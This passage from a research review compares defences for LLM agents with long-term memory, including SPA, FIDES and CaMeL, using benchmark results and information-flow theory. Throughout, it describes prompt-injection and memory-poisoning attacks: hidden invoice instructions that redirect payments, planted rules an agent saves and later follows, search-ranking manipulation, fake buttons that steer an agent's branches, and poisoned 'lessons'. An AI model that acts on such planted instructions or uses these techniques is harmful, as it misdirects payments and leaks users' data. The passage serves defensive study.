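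If any step fails the check, SPA ends the request with an error before running any tools. It sends the planner no details of the failure and doesn't request another plan, which rules out leaks like the one through CaMeL's retry loop. However, this also means the planner can't repair a plan that failed because of a small mistake.

The design also avoids the label creep that affects a FIDES planner once it reads an untrusted memory. SPA's planner reads only descriptions, so one plan can retrieve an untrusted note to show the user and also make a payment with trusted values, without the note affecting the payment's label.

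### Tuesday's payment in SPA

When the user asks the agent to pay yesterday's invoice, the planner finds the matching description and might write this plan, shown here in simplified form:

```
invoice = retrieve("acme_invoice")
send_money(to = invoice.account, amount = invoice.amount)
display("Acme's invoice is paid.")
```

The checker gives `invoice` its stored label, private and untrusted. The payment tool requires trusted inputs, so the checker rejects the plan and no money moves. The hidden instruction had no effect either, because neither day's planner read it. SPA therefore stops both the delayed planning attack and the delayed execution attack.

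SPA would also block payment of a genuine invoice, and the user cannot easily get around this. Suppose the user types Acme's correct account number on Tuesday and asks the agent to take only the amount from the invoice. The plan still fails, because SPA sets one trust requirement for the whole tool and a single untrusted argument violates it. FIDES lets a developer relax the rule for particular arguments. SPA would also reject "if the invoice is overdue, pay 500 euros to this account", because the invoice's due date decides whether the payment happens. If the user typed every detail, the payment could go through, but the memory would contribute nothing. SPA has no endorsement step that could raise the label after a check.

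SPA hides both the values and their labels from the planner. Suppose the memory holds two account numbers for Acme, one from the company's own accounting system and one from an email. The planner sees only their descriptions, and if it picks the number from the email, the request fails without a second attempt. A developer could safely add the integrity label to each description, since labels come from a short fixed list.

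The agent can still answer questions about the invoice. Text for the user goes through a separate check, and if an item breaks the display rule, SPA blanks out that item and shows the rest.

### AgentDojo-MQ

AgentDojo resets the agent after every task, so Girrens and Wang built a version with several requests per task, AgentDojo-MQ. They converted all 97 AgentDojo tasks in these steps:

1. They drew a graph by hand for each task, showing which results later actions need.
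2. Software cut each graph into two to five turns. Every task has at least one later step that needs an earlier result, though some turns hold separate parts of the task that need nothing from before.
3. GPT-5.4 wrote one user message per turn, and the researchers edited messages that gave away an answer or were ambiguous.

In one example, the user asks the agent to find a networking event in the calendar, then asks in a separate message for the invitees' email addresses. The agent should retrieve the event from memory without searching the calendar again. The tools, planted attacks and final scoring are the same as in AgentDojo.

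The attacks came from AgentDojo too. They hide instructions in tool results, and the attacker knows the exact sequence of tools needed. Each version had 949 attack runs. The planner and the quarantined model were both GPT-5.4 nano, a small OpenAI model.

| Setting | Tasks completed, one request | Attacks that succeeded, one request | Tasks completed, several requests | Attacks that succeeded, several requests |
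|---|---|---|---|---|
| No label checks, planner sees stored values | not tested | not tested | 65.9% | 0.6% |
| No label checks, planner sees descriptions | 53.0% | 0.4% | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Label checks, planner sees descriptions | 29.0% | 0.0% | 35.3% | 0.2% |

*Completion rates are for runs without an attack.*

#### Hiding values cost little

Letting the planner read the stored values raised the completion rate only slightly, from 62.5% to 65.9%. The agent completed four more of the 16 banking tasks but four fewer of the 20 travel tasks. In two of the travel failures, the planner wrote its plan in the wrong format. With so few tasks, this difference could easily be due to chance.

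Girrens and Wang also checked whether a later plan retrieved the earlier result it needed. When the earlier turn had saved a suitable result, the plan retrieved it in 95.4% of cases without label checks and 89.9% with them. The earlier turn had saved nothing suitable in about a sixth of cases without checks and a fifth with them. Counting these cases as failures lowers the rates to 80.1% and 73.4%. Most of the missed reuse therefore came from failed earlier steps rather than from planners choosing the wrong description.

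These rates are higher than the completion rates because a plan can retrieve the right result and still do the wrong thing with it. But they show that a planner can usually pick the right memory from a description when the list is short.

#### Label checks cost a lot

Turning on label checks cut the completion rate from 62.5% to 35.3%. On the original single-request tasks, the rate fell by 24 percentage points. The checker rejected about 45% of runs on AgentDojo-MQ and 53% on AgentDojo, typically because a plan passed untrusted tool output to a tool that required trusted input. Many AgentDojo tasks require this, such as when a user wants the agent to act on the contents of an email.

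The 35.3% may be slightly too high. Five banking tasks count as complete when the agent does nothing, because the scoring depends only on the final state of the simulated bank. An agent could get credit for those tasks even if the checker rejected its plan.

Completion rates were higher with several requests than with one, possibly because shorter plans are easier to write. But Girrens and Wang point out that the two versions also differ in wording, conversation history and scoring, so the gap does not measure the benefit of memory.

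### How strong is the evidence?

SPA's attack success rate of 0.2% is two runs out of 949. Girrens and Wang report two travel runs that AgentDojo scored as successful attacks although SPA had rejected the plan, so the true figure is probably zero. The single-request test gives clearer evidence that the checks matter. They stopped four attacks that succeeded without them, all on the same banking task. In these attacks, the quarantined model read the injected text, and its output went into tools that should have accepted only trusted data. Three of the attacks caused unauthorised transfers and one changed a password.

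AgentDojo-MQ does not show how well SPA resists attacks designed for memory, because its attack rarely succeeded even without SPA's protection. When the planner could read every stored value, which SPA is meant to prevent, the attack success rate was only 0.6%. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that the attack "only weakly exercises delayed memory poisoning" and call for attacks written to test it.

Gadgil and colleagues explain the difference with an analogy from web security. In a reflected attack, a malicious script affects a visitor only when a particular request carries it, whereas in a stored attack the website saves the script and serves it again later. AgentDojo's attacks are reflected. Their text contains instructions for the agent to act on during the current task, and it is not designed to persist in memory or to take effect on a particular later request.

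Stored attacks work much better against ordinary agents. In *MemHarmBench*, Wang, Feng and colleagues (2026) tested four combinations of agent and model on 288 cases. In one case, an imported note tells the agent to name a company called Harbor Clearing as the recipient in future expense summaries. After checking that the agent had saved this rule, the researchers deleted the note, started a new session and made an ordinary request for a summary. The records named a different recipient, Northstar Travel. When an outside document had planted a rule and the agent had saved it, the agent followed the rule 59% to 76% of the time. In about 56% of these cases on average, the agent also finished the user's task and behaved normally, so the user would have had little reason to suspect anything.

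These rates favor the attacks because they exclude cases where the agent never saved the rule, and because the request in the first session explicitly asked the agent to adopt a convention. Wang and colleagues did not test SPA. SPA's planner would not read the note, so the rule could not change the plan. But if the plan passed the note to the quarantined model along with the expense records, the summary could still name Harbor Clearing. The summary's untrusted label would keep it out of a payment tool, but the user might still see it.

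Using GPT-5.4 nano as the planner probably lowered the completion rates. OpenAI's *Introducing GPT-5.4 mini and nano* recommends nano for sorting, data extraction and simple supporting tasks, and describes systems in which a larger model plans while small ones do narrower jobs. On Toolathlon, a test of tool use, nano scored 35.5% and the full GPT-5.4 scored 54.6%. A stronger planner would make fewer mistakes and, without checks, might complete far more than 62.5% of tasks. It would gain less with checks on, because no plan can make an untrusted account number trusted. The gap between completion rates with and without checks might therefore grow.

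Each test also lasted only two to five turns and produced a handful of stored results. The researchers made references to earlier messages clear, so the planner seldom had to search hard for the right result. An assistant used daily for a year could have thousands of entries, many with similar descriptions.

### Finding a memory by its content

A planner that writes a description before the agent fetches the data can record why the agent wanted the data, but not what it contains. Suppose the agent checks for new mail from Acme every week. Every entry might have the description "latest email from Acme", including the one that announced a price rise. If the user later asks when Acme raised its prices, the planner can't tell from the descriptions which entry to use.

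Coding agents face a similar problem with skills, which are saved procedures that an agent can load when needed. The agent usually sees only each skill's name and description. In *SkillRouter*, Zheng, Zhang and colleagues (2026) tested how well search software could pick the right skill for a task from about 80,000. The best off-the-shelf search system they tested ranked a correct skill first for 68% of tasks when it could read the skills' full text, but for only 24% with just names and descriptions. Across the systems they compared, hiding the full text lowered this rate by 37 to 44 percentage points.

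A longer list of descriptions also contains more distractions. In a small experiment in *Lost in Implicit Routing* (2026), three models worked on ten tasks with 1,000 irrelevant skills on the list, and they loaded no skill in 62.2% of runs. Replacing the irrelevant entries with meaningless placeholders of about the same length reduced that share to 23.6%. Length alone was therefore a smaller problem than plausible alternatives, and a long memory full of supplier emails would contain many plausible alternatives.

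Better descriptions help, but writing them requires reading the content. Zheng and colleagues had a model read the full text of each correct skill and rewrite its description, which raised the success rate from about 25% to between 53% and 61%. That was still 7 to 21 points below searching the full text. In SPA, a model-written description of a stored email would carry the same risk as a free-text summary.

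A safer compromise is to let the quarantined model fill in fields that software can check, such as a date, an amount or a category from a fixed list. The planner could then search for "Acme, price change, June".

#### Memories that matter unexpectedly

Sometimes nothing in a request points to the memory it needs. In one example from *Keep It InMind* (Li, Du and colleagues, 2026), a user with a tree-nut allergy asks for a macaron recipe. Macarons contain almond flour, but neither the request nor the memory mentions this. The researchers wrote 125 such tasks and tested six memory systems, all of which search for stored text that resembles the request. The best applied the right memory in 14.4% of tasks, and a plain text search did so in 16.0%. When the researchers gave the same model the memory directly, it succeeded in 84.0%, so it had the knowledge to make the connection. A simple profile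 that was always in view had a success rate of 68.8%.

SPA should do reasonably well if the user mentioned the allergy in an earlier request, because the planner sees those requests directly. If the allergy was in an email from a clinic, the planner would see only something like "latest message from the clinic", and would have little reason to retrieve it for a recipe, even though it knows about the almond flour. The quarantined model can read the email only if the plan passes it along. A cautious plan could pass every stored health message to the quarantined model whenever the user asks about food. That would take more time and money, and the recipe would become untrusted, which does no harm if the agent only displays it.

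#### Searching without reading

SPA's language has no search step. Each retrieve step names one stored result, so a plan that compares 500 emails needs 500 retrieve steps. A developer could add a tool that searches the stored values and returns the best match as a variable, which the planner would handle without reading. This would solve much of the problem of finding memories by content, but it would also let that content influence which memory the agent uses.

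### The choice of memory as an untrusted influence

In SPA as published, an attacker has little control over which memory a plan retrieves, because the planner chooses from descriptions the attacker didn't write. But a tool result in the wrong format ends the whole request, and SPA saves results only from requests that succeed. A website could therefore keep a result off Tuesday's list by deliberately returning broken data, though it could not add one.

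An agent that searches its memory by content gives an attacker much more influence. In *Hidden in Memory*, Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues (2026) studied documents that trick an assistant into saving a false memory about its user. They placed the false memories among harmless ones and had a separate model select the relevant ones for each new conversation. The model picked the planted memory for 90% to 98% of requests on a related topic and for 3% to 18% of unrelated ones. Any working search would return a memory on the right topic, so an attacker who chooses the topic largely chooses when the memory appears. The attacker can improve the odds by guessing likely requests and rewording the memory to resemble them closely.

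Retrieving harmless memories can also bring in a planted one. *MemoryDojo* (2026) describes a case in which a search returned 12 facts, none from the attacker. The memory system then added seven linked records of past sessions for context, and one contained the attacker's text.

If each entry keeps its own label, the software will recognise a planted memory as untrusted when a search returns it. The harder case is when untrusted memories change which trusted ones the search returns. Suppose the user gave the agent Acme's account number in March and a corrected number in June, and the search tool returns the ten best matches. The March number ranks first and the June correction ninth. An attacker then sends emails that cause the agent to store two new notes about Acme's account, which push the correction to eleventh place. Software removes the untrusted notes from the results, and the agent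 pays the March account. Every value in the payment is trusted, but the attacker determined which account number the agent used.

*Ghost in the Agent* calls this implicit control influence. NeuroTaint, the paper's auditing tool, might still miss this example, because it tests only sources it can trace to the call, and the software removed the attacker's notes before the agent saw them.

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) describes a related attack, called branch steering, on agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen. The planner writes a fixed plan with branches for different situations. An attacker draws a fake button, the model that reads the screen reports it as real, and the agent takes a branch the planner meant for another situation. The attacker can therefore choose which of the planner's steps the agent runs, without adding new ones.

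SPA has a strict rule for this kind of choice when it is part of the plan. Suppose the user has stored one trusted account for euro payments and another for pound payments, and the plan picks between them by the currency on the invoice. The invoice is untrusted, so $pc$ is untrusted in both branches. The retrieve formula combines $pc$ with the stored label, so the account number becomes untrusted even though the user typed it. The checker then blocks the payment.

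A search tool makes the same kind of choice outside the plan, where $pc$ does not record it. To be as strict as SPA's rule for conditions, the software would have to give each search result the combined label of every entry that could have affected the ranking. A single untrusted note in the store would then make every result untrusted.

The alternative is to filter by label before ranking, as in IFDB's Query by Label, so that the search in the example returns both of the user's numbers. A plan could run one search over trusted entries for values it will act on and another over all entries for material it will only show the user. The planner can write both searches without reading any results, because it only needs to know how each search's results will be used.

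## Which abilities are lost when the planner cannot read untrusted memories?

SPA's planner can choose Monday's invoice from a list of descriptions and pass it to a tool by name without reading it. That is enough if the planner can decide every step in advance, but not if the agent's next step depends on the memory's contents. Costa and colleagues described this difference in their work on FIDES.

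### Data-independent and data-dependent tasks

Costa and colleagues define a task as a user's request, a list of tools and a set $D$ of possible states of the data that the tools can reach. For each state $d$, let $S(d)$ be the set of action sequences that would complete the task, counting tool calls and the final reply. The task is data-independent if

$$\bigcap_{d \in D} S(d) \neq \varnothing,$$

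which means that at least one sequence works whatever the data says. Otherwise the task is data-dependent.

The task "Send my three latest emails to a colleague on Slack" is data-independent because its steps don't depend on what the emails say. The agent reads the emails and sends them on, and the planner can refer to their text by name. Summarising them first adds a call to the quarantined model, but the task is still data-independent.

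The request "Complete the tasks due today in my to-do app" is data-dependent. The list may contain a bill to pay one day and a meeting to arrange the next, and no single sequence of steps handles both. The planner cannot finish its plan until it has some information about the list.

Some data-dependent tasks need very little information. In one of Costa and colleagues' examples, the user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if there is one. FIDES can do this without showing the planner the emails:

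1. The planner reads the emails into a hidden variable.
2. It asks the quarantined model whether any email requests a meeting, and software allows only "yes" or "no" as the answer.
3. The planner reads the answer.
4. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the date, time and participants into another hidden variable.
5. The planner passes that variable to the calendar tool.

An answer can be limited to a fixed set of options, such as yes or no. Costa and colleagues also suggest a short menu of actions, such as scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply or forwarding the email. As with Willison's checked answers, an attacker could influence the choice but not insert an instruction. An answer chosen from $n$ options carries at most $\log_2 n$ bits of information, or one bit for a yes or no, so a developer's policy can let the agent act on it.

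A planner that cannot read untrusted memories can choose only among options that someone foresaw. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) points out that long tasks can change course when an agent discovers, for example, that an authorisation has expired. If the planner didn't write a branch for this before reading anything, it has none to follow, even if the quarantined model reads the notice correctly.

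### How plans use different kinds of memory

The same distinction applies to memory, because a later plan may need only a stored value, a choice between known options, or new steps.

| Memory | What the plan needs from it | What a planner can do without reading it | Common sources |
|---|---|---|---|
| An address, account number or document | The value itself | Pass it to a tool by name | The user, emails, files |
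| A preference, such as train or plane | One of a few options | Receive a fixed choice | The user, or a model's guess about the user |
| A project's conventions | Rules about wording and about steps | Have the quarantined model follow the rules about wording | Project files, colleagues, outside contributors |
| A lesson from a failed attempt | A change to the steps | Use it only if the planner already had that alternative | Error messages, web pages, other tool results |
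| A saved procedure | The steps themselves | Very little | The agent's past runs, downloaded files |

The use of **stored values** is affected least. The planner can still retrieve an address and pass it to a tool, though a policy may block an untrusted value from directing a payment. However, the planner can no longer detect that it has retrieved the wrong value. In experiments with CaMeL agents, Peters-Gill and colleagues saw an agent request data about one machine or period, receive data about a nearby one, and carry on, because the planner had written its program before the reply arrived. An agent could similarly retrieve Acme's May invoice when the user meant June's. The plan can include a step in which the quarantined model checks the month, but only if the planner anticipates that mistake.

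**Preferences** usually survive too. If a preference only fills in a detail, such as an aisle seat, the planner can pass it by name. If the choice between the railway's tool and the airline's depends on the preference, the quarantined model can return "train" or "plane". This works even for a complicated preference, such as taking the train unless the journey lasts more than five hours, because the quarantined model can read the whole note along with the trip details.

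An agent whose planner cannot read untrusted memories can still follow some saved conventions, but not those that change its plan. A coding assistant might have a saved note that a project uses British spelling and that developers must rebuild the database client before running the tests. The quarantined model can read the spelling rule while it drafts an error message, although the draft is then untrusted. The rebuild rule adds a step to the plan, so it has no effect unless the planner knows about it.

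**Lessons and procedures** are meant to change the plan. *ARGUS* (2026), a defence that audits an agent's decisions before it acts, lists memory records and installed skills among the known routes for prompt injection because an agent's next action can depend on them, which is also why they are useful.

### What FIDES loses on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's 97 tasks by hand. The table converts their percentages into numbers of tasks.

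| Environment | Data-independent | Data-independent, but a quarantined model must read something | Data-dependent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 19 | 19 | 2 |
| Travel | 0 | 18 | 2 |
| Banking | 3 | 6 | 7 |
| Slack | 4 | 8 | 9 |
| Total | 26 | 51 | 20 |

About four-fifths of the tasks therefore don't require the plan to change after the agent sees the data. This favours FIDES, but the agent still lost a good deal. The next table shows the average completion rate across the four environments with GPT-4o and no attacks.

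| Planner | Without policy checks | With policy checks |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary planner that reads everything | 84.3% | 41.9% |
| Planner that can only pass variables | 46.5% | 45.9% |
| FIDES | 60.6% | 50.0% |

With the policy checks applied to both agents, FIDES completed 8 percentage points more tasks than the ordinary planner. With o1, a stronger reasoning model from OpenAI, it completed 16 points more. The ordinary planner does badly under these checks because once it reads an untrusted email, it cannot make consequential calls.

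FIDES with GPT-4o scored about 34 points lower than an unprotected agent. It trailed by roughly 24 points even with the policy checks off, so that part of the loss came from the extra work of handling hidden values. The policy accounted for the remaining 10 or 11 points. With o1 and no checks, the gap shrank to 6.3 points, so better models can recover much of the loss from handling hidden values, but not the loss from correct refusals.

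In many of the failed banking tasks, the user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. Reading the file made the context untrusted, so the software blocked the payment or the change of address. Costa and colleagues count these failures as intended. But to a user, asking an agent to follow instructions in a file is an ordinary request, and a saved procedure is a file of instructions that the agent reads later.

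In another task, the user asked the agent to change a password if a recent transaction looked suspicious. FIDES hid the transactions' descriptions but showed their amounts. The planner judged a large payment suspicious from the amount alone and changed the password. AgentDojo counted the task as complete, so its score does not show that the planner had guessed.

### What a fixed plan costs CaMeL

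CaMeL's fixed program gives it fewer chances to adapt than FIDES has. Peters-Gill and colleagues measured the resulting loss on 112 tasks from AssetOpsBench, a benchmark in which a coordinating agent and four specialists answer questions about industrial equipment. They ran the same models with and without CaMeL and switched off all data policies, so the loss came from the fixed plan alone. Across five models, CaMeL completed 21.6 percentage points fewer tasks on average. For the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, the loss was 13.4 points.

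Most failures occurred because the agent discovered partway through that it needed a step the program didn't include. Stronger planners probably lost less because they anticipated more of these steps. Adding the two rules for communication between agents lowered scores by only another 3.2 points on average, so keeping labels on notes passed between sessions may also lower scores much less than the fixed plan does.

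Peters-Gill and colleagues also advise against carrying a conversation over when one agent calls another again, because the earlier exchange may contain text derived from untrusted data. Under this rule, a specialist agent would start every job without knowing what went wrong in the last one.

Results on AgentDojo vary widely with the set-up. When Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5 and no attacks, it completed 49 of the 97 tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing defence, reports 29 of 97 for an adapted version of CaMeL and 59 for its own system, which keeps the ordinary agent loop. In the same test, none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL. *The Devil is in the Context* (2026) reports 27.5% utility for CaMeL on its own new attack cases, with 2.5% of attacks succeeding. PromptArmor, which uses a language model to find and remove injected instructions,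 kept 90% utility but let 7.5% of attacks succeed. A user might reasonably accept PromptArmor's higher attack rate when reading the news but prefer CaMeL for paying bills.

#### Open-ended tasks

CaMeL did worst on tasks that change as the agent works. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) contains 60 tasks in shopping, software development and daily life that each require the agent to adapt its plan. For example, the agent may have to fetch a one-time code from the user's email, or follow a notice on a checkout page to log in first. CaMeL completed none of the tasks with any of the four models in the main comparison. Without a defence, GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude 3.5 Sonnet completed between 52% and 60%, and Llama 3.3 70B completed 10%.

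These tasks all depend on what CaMeL cannot do, so a very low score was likely. The score of zero over 240 attempts may also reflect how well the software suited the new tools, since CaMeL needs a policy and an output description for each tool. The researchers also told every agent to finish without asking the user for confirmation, because undefended agents often stopped to ask. In normal use, an agent can deal with an unexpected step by asking the user.

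DRIFT, a less rigid defence in the same study, starts from a plan but uses a second check to approve changes to it. With the three stronger models, it completed 30% to 37% of the tasks, and 0.8% to 3.1% of attacks succeeded. Without a defence, 12% to 38% of attacks on those models succeeded.

#### Agents that operate a computer

An agent that operates software through its graphical interface seems to need to see the screen at every step. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* tested whether a planner could work without seeing it by having the planner write a fixed program with many branches. A typical program made 41 tool calls and had 40 branches, compared with about 5 calls and 4 branches for CaMeL on AgentDojo.

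The researchers tested the isolated planner on OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday tasks in programs such as Chrome and LibreOffice. They used 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had completed without this protection. With the isolated planner, the model completed 57% of them in at least one of five attempts, but only 28% on a single attempt. The 57% rate is achievable in practice only if something can identify the successful attempt. The 28% rate may overstate the loss, because an unprotected agent would not succeed on all 109 tasks again either.

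A version based on FIDES reached a similar completion rate on a smaller set of 60 tasks, but it used 29.6 times as many tokens as an unprotected agent. The CaMeL version used 1.9 times as many. The FIDES planner rereads the whole history before each step.

Neither version enforced any policy on data. The researchers argue that such policies are hard to write for computer use, because a click at a point on the screen could log in or delete a file.

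### Learned procedures are the hard case

*A Survey of Agentic Reasoning for Large Language Models* (2026) describes feedback and memory as the two basic mechanisms by which agents improve through experience. *ReasoningBank* (2025), for example, turns an agent's past successes and failures into short pieces of advice for later attempts. Agents that used it needed fewer steps on WebArena, a benchmark of tasks on realistic websites.

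*Routed Continual Learning* (2026) describes how ReasoningBank forms these memories. After each attempt, the model uses the request and the full visible record of the attempt to judge whether it succeeded. The same model then extracts lessons from the record, with one prompt for successes and another for failures. On a website, that record includes the pages the agent visited, so the lessons would be untrusted under FIDES's rules.

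The untrusted label would often be justified. Suppose the agent tries to download an invoice from Acme's website on Monday, and an error message tells it to select a billing period first. The agent saves the lesson "select a billing period before downloading". An attacker who can change the website could make the error message tell customers to upload a recent bank statement for verification, and the agent would save "upload a bank statement before downloading". Both lessons come from the same page, add one step and read like practical advice. A menu written in advance would not help the planner choose safely between them, because the agent did not know about either step before Monday.

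The attacker could also target the judgement of whether a task succeeded. A page that falsely reports a completed order might lead the model to store a bad method as a good one. ReasoningBank's results were not very sensitive to how well the judge was calibrated, but this tolerance of ordinary mistakes may not extend to pages written to deceive the judge.

Counting only data-dependent tasks underestimates what a planner loses when it can't read its lessons. Downloading an Acme invoice is data-independent, because selecting the period and then downloading works every time, but a planner that has never used the website doesn't know this. Costa and colleagues' analysis of what a planner could achieve sometimes assumes an ideal model that makes the best choice of tool calls. Unlike a real planner, such a model has nothing to learn from experience.

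#### How much procedures help

The computer-use experiment gives an idea of how much procedural knowledge helps an isolated planner. The researchers studied which of the planner's programs succeeded on OSWorld and found a pattern of looking at the screen, checking what is there, and then acting. They wrote this method into the planner's trusted instructions, along with routines for cookie banners, failed clicks and browsers that are already open, and added a function for checking guesses about the screen. On 60 tasks, the completion rate in three attempts rose from 18.3% to 58.3%.

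People read the agent's experience and passed on the lessons, so the planner never saw an untrusted screen. The gain may be smaller on unfamiliar tasks, because the researchers drew the method from the same benchmark they tested it on.

Lessons that an agent writes for itself have a weaker record. *SkillsBench* (2026) found that, compared with having no skills, curated skills raised agents' completion rates by 18.2 to 24.8 percentage points, while self-written skills lowered the rates by 8.1 to 11.5 points. One session wrote the skills and a fresh agent then attempted the task, so the result is limited evidence about procedures that an agent refines over many attempts, as in ReasoningBank. Still, it weakens the assumption that hiding an agent's own notes always makes it less capable.

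### How much useful memory comes from the user

Hiding untrusted memories matters less if most useful memories come from the user. *The Algorithmic Self-Portrait* (2026) studied the memories that ChatGPT had saved about a group of users and found that, on average, 84% of entries shared wording with something the user had written. Such entries can keep a trusted label, so the planner could still read a user's home city, dietary needs and preferred tone before it plans. Curated skills can also be trusted if the developer controls them.

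A memory can share the user's wording without recording what the user meant. One participant asked for bands like Nirvana, and ChatGPT saved "User likes Nirvana", a reasonable guess that the user never stated. *Knowing the User Is Not Knowing What We Established* (2026) found that when two personal agents, Hermes and OpenJarvis, stored a proposal the user had never accepted, they recorded it as confirmed information or a fact about the user in 86% to 100% of cases. OpenJarvis kept the limits on a proposal, such as the situation it applied to, in only 4% to 11% of cases. Software that trusts everything saved from a chat would give such entries the user's authority. Saving the user's exact words separately from a model's interpretation would avoid this.

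The ChatGPT study also describes people chatting, while an agent with access to a mailbox and the web reads far more text from strangers. A personal assistant that mostly books travel and answers questions would probably lose little if its planner could not read untrusted memories. An agent that maintains the same software for months depends more on error messages, outside documentation and lessons from failed attempts, and its planner could not read much of this unless someone first vouched for it.

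### What current benchmarks leave out

Li and colleagues argue that standard benchmarks make rigid planning look better than it is. By their count, only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan, while Costa and colleagues classify 20 as data-dependent. The counts probably differ because a fixed program can handle some data-dependent tasks. For example, a planner can write both branches of "create an event if someone requests a meeting" in advance.

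AgentDojo also contains few helpful instructions from third parties, so a defence loses little by ignoring every instruction it finds. Its tasks average 3.5 steps, against 7.1 in AgentDyn, and short tasks with complete instructions give an agent little to learn. The benchmark can also understate what an agent can do. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that Claude Fable 5 refused 52 of the 97 tasks even without an attack, possibly because it recognised the setting as a prompt injection test.

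Real requests are often incomplete. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026), a benchmark that adapts its attacks to each defence, sorts tasks by how much the user specifies. The user may specify the action and all its details, specify the action but leave the agent to find the details, or let the content determine the action. Attacks succeeded much more often on requests that left the action open. These requests are also the hardest for a planner to complete without reading the content, so a benchmark with few of them understates both how vulnerable ordinary agents are and how much ability they lose when protected.

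AgentDojo-MQ tests whether an agent can reuse an earlier result, but not whether it learns from an earlier failure. ReasoningBank and SkillsBench measure whether stored advice helps an agent, but not when its planner cannot read untrusted text.

A direct test would run one agent through the same series of related tasks with no memory, with unrestricted memory and with labelled memory that hides untrusted entries from the planner. If $U$ is the completion rate on the later tasks, the share of learning that survives the protection is

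$$\frac{U_{\text{labelled}} - U_{\text{none}}}{U_{\text{unrestricted}} - U_{\text{none}}}.$$

If experience raised the success rate from 50% to 65% with unrestricted memory but only to 53% with labelled memory, the agent would have kept a fifth of the improvement. None of these studies reports this fraction. The test would also need attacks that plant false lessons, because unrestricted memory might lose its advantage when some lessons come from an attacker.

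## How can an untrusted memory come to be trusted?

An agent can act on more of its memory if someone endorses the untrusted parts. Endorsement is a deliberate, authorised step that raises the integrity label of a piece of data. For example, if the user checks the account number on Acme's invoice and confirms it, the software can change the number's label to trusted, and the payment tool will accept it. IFDB's declassifying views play the same role for confidentiality.

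Declassification and endorsement both deliberately break the ordinary flow rules, so a system that allows them needs other rules about when they are safe. An attacker who can trigger an endorsement, or choose what it applies to, can get malicious data marked as trusted without having to defeat the labels. In *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control*, Cecchetti, Myers and Arden (2017) set two conditions, robust declassification and transparent endorsement, and a system that meets both has nonmalleable information flow.

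### The two conditions

Robust declassification means that an attacker has no influence over what the system releases. Suppose Acme disputes a payment, and the user authorises the agent to send Acme the private record of it. If a line in Acme's email could determine which record the agent attaches, the sender could exploit that authorisation to obtain records of the user's salary payments. Costa and colleagues point out that FIDES's rule for consequential actions gives a form of this protection, because private data can leave only when the decision to send it is trusted.

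Transparent endorsement forbids endorsing data that its author could not have read. Cecchetti and colleagues use a sealed-bid auction to show how someone can write data they can't read. Alice and Bob send bids to an auctioneer, and each bid has a label that prevents anyone from reading it until both of them agree. Bob submits "Alice's bid plus one". Software can compute this without showing Bob the number, and the result is as secret as Alice's bid, so it breaks no confidentiality rule. Once the auctioneer endorses Bob's bid as genuine, he wins by the smallest possible margin. The fix is to loosen the labels so that each bidder can read their own bid. Copying Alice's number into Bob's bid would then reveal it to Bob, so the confidentiality rules would block it.

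The Acme invoice can produce the same problem. Suppose the quarantined model reads the invoice together with the user's private notes about suppliers, and extracts a payment reference. The invoice contains a hidden instruction to use a rival supplier's price as the reference. The user sees "reference 48200", which looks normal, and confirms it. When the payment goes through, the rival's price appears on the attacker's bank statement.

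Software can catch this if labels name people instead of using two levels. Costa and colleagues describe an integrity label that lists everyone who may have influenced a value, alongside the list of its permitted readers. If $W(x)$ is the set of people who may have influenced $x$ and $R(x)$ is the set who may read it, a simplified test for transparent endorsement is

$$W(x) \subseteq R(x).$$

A reference extracted from the invoice alone passes, because Acme wrote the invoice and can read it, but one extracted from the invoice and the notes fails, because Acme may have influenced it but is not allowed to read the notes. With two-level labels, both references would be "private, untrusted", and software could not tell them apart. Cecchetti and colleagues built a type system, a set of rules for checking a program before it runs, that never allows data to become public or trusted if an attacker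 can influence it but not read it.

In *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real-Ideal Paradigm*, Kanniwadi and Myers (2026) proved that, for programs that pass their checker, any attack by a powerful attacker is equivalent to one by a weaker attacker who can interact only with the points where the program declassifies or endorses data. Reviewers can therefore concentrate on those points. The proof covers programs in a small language, so for an agent it could apply at most to the software around the models.

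Neither condition tests whether data is true. The attacker knows the false account number, so endorsing it is transparent. Louck presents TMA-NM as an application of nonmalleable information flow to memory, but describes transparent endorsement differently, as a rule that untrusted data cannot be used to endorse itself. TMA-NM's approval procedure checks who vouches for a value but not whether the value's author could read it. It would prevent the invoice from being used to approve its own account number, but not the leak through the payment reference.

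### Confirmation by the user

A user can approve either an action or a value. TMA-NM's single-use approvals are for actions. A payment, for example, goes ahead only if it matches the approval exactly, so nobody can change the account after the user approves it. The approval does not change the label on the saved account number, so the agent has to ask again for the next payment. If the user endorses the statement "this is Acme's account", the agent needs to ask only once, but a mistaken endorsement lasts until someone corrects it.

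An approval can also become outdated before the agent uses it. EffectMatch, a system presented in *Beyond Approved Actions* (Zhang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), ties each approval to the state of the task when the user gave it. In the paper's example, a user approves marking an invoice as paid, but the approval becomes void when the company blocks the supplier. EffectMatch also marks an approval as used before it starts the action, so the agent cannot reuse it for a second payment after a crash. It then compares the resulting changes with what the user approved. In tests on twelve business tasks with deliberately introduced faults, it rejected every incorrect result.

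These checks don't help if the user approves without looking, and there is good evidence that people do. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a study of 1,053 paid testers in which one permission prompt per session contained a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% refused it, and the refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic published these figures to support replacing the prompts with its automatic checker, and the testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than someone sending their own money. But the decline is hard to explain except by habit or fatigue.

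Studies of working programmers also suggest that people check AI agents' work less carefully as it becomes familiar. In *Habituation at the Gate* (2026), reviewers' approval rate for code written by AI agents rose 14.5 percentage points from the first tenth of their reviews to the last, while approval of code written by people fell. The reviewers might have learned that the agents' code was usually sound, so the extra approvals were not necessarily mistakes. In *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), however, practitioners described clicking through familiar prompts and skipping reviews under time pressure.

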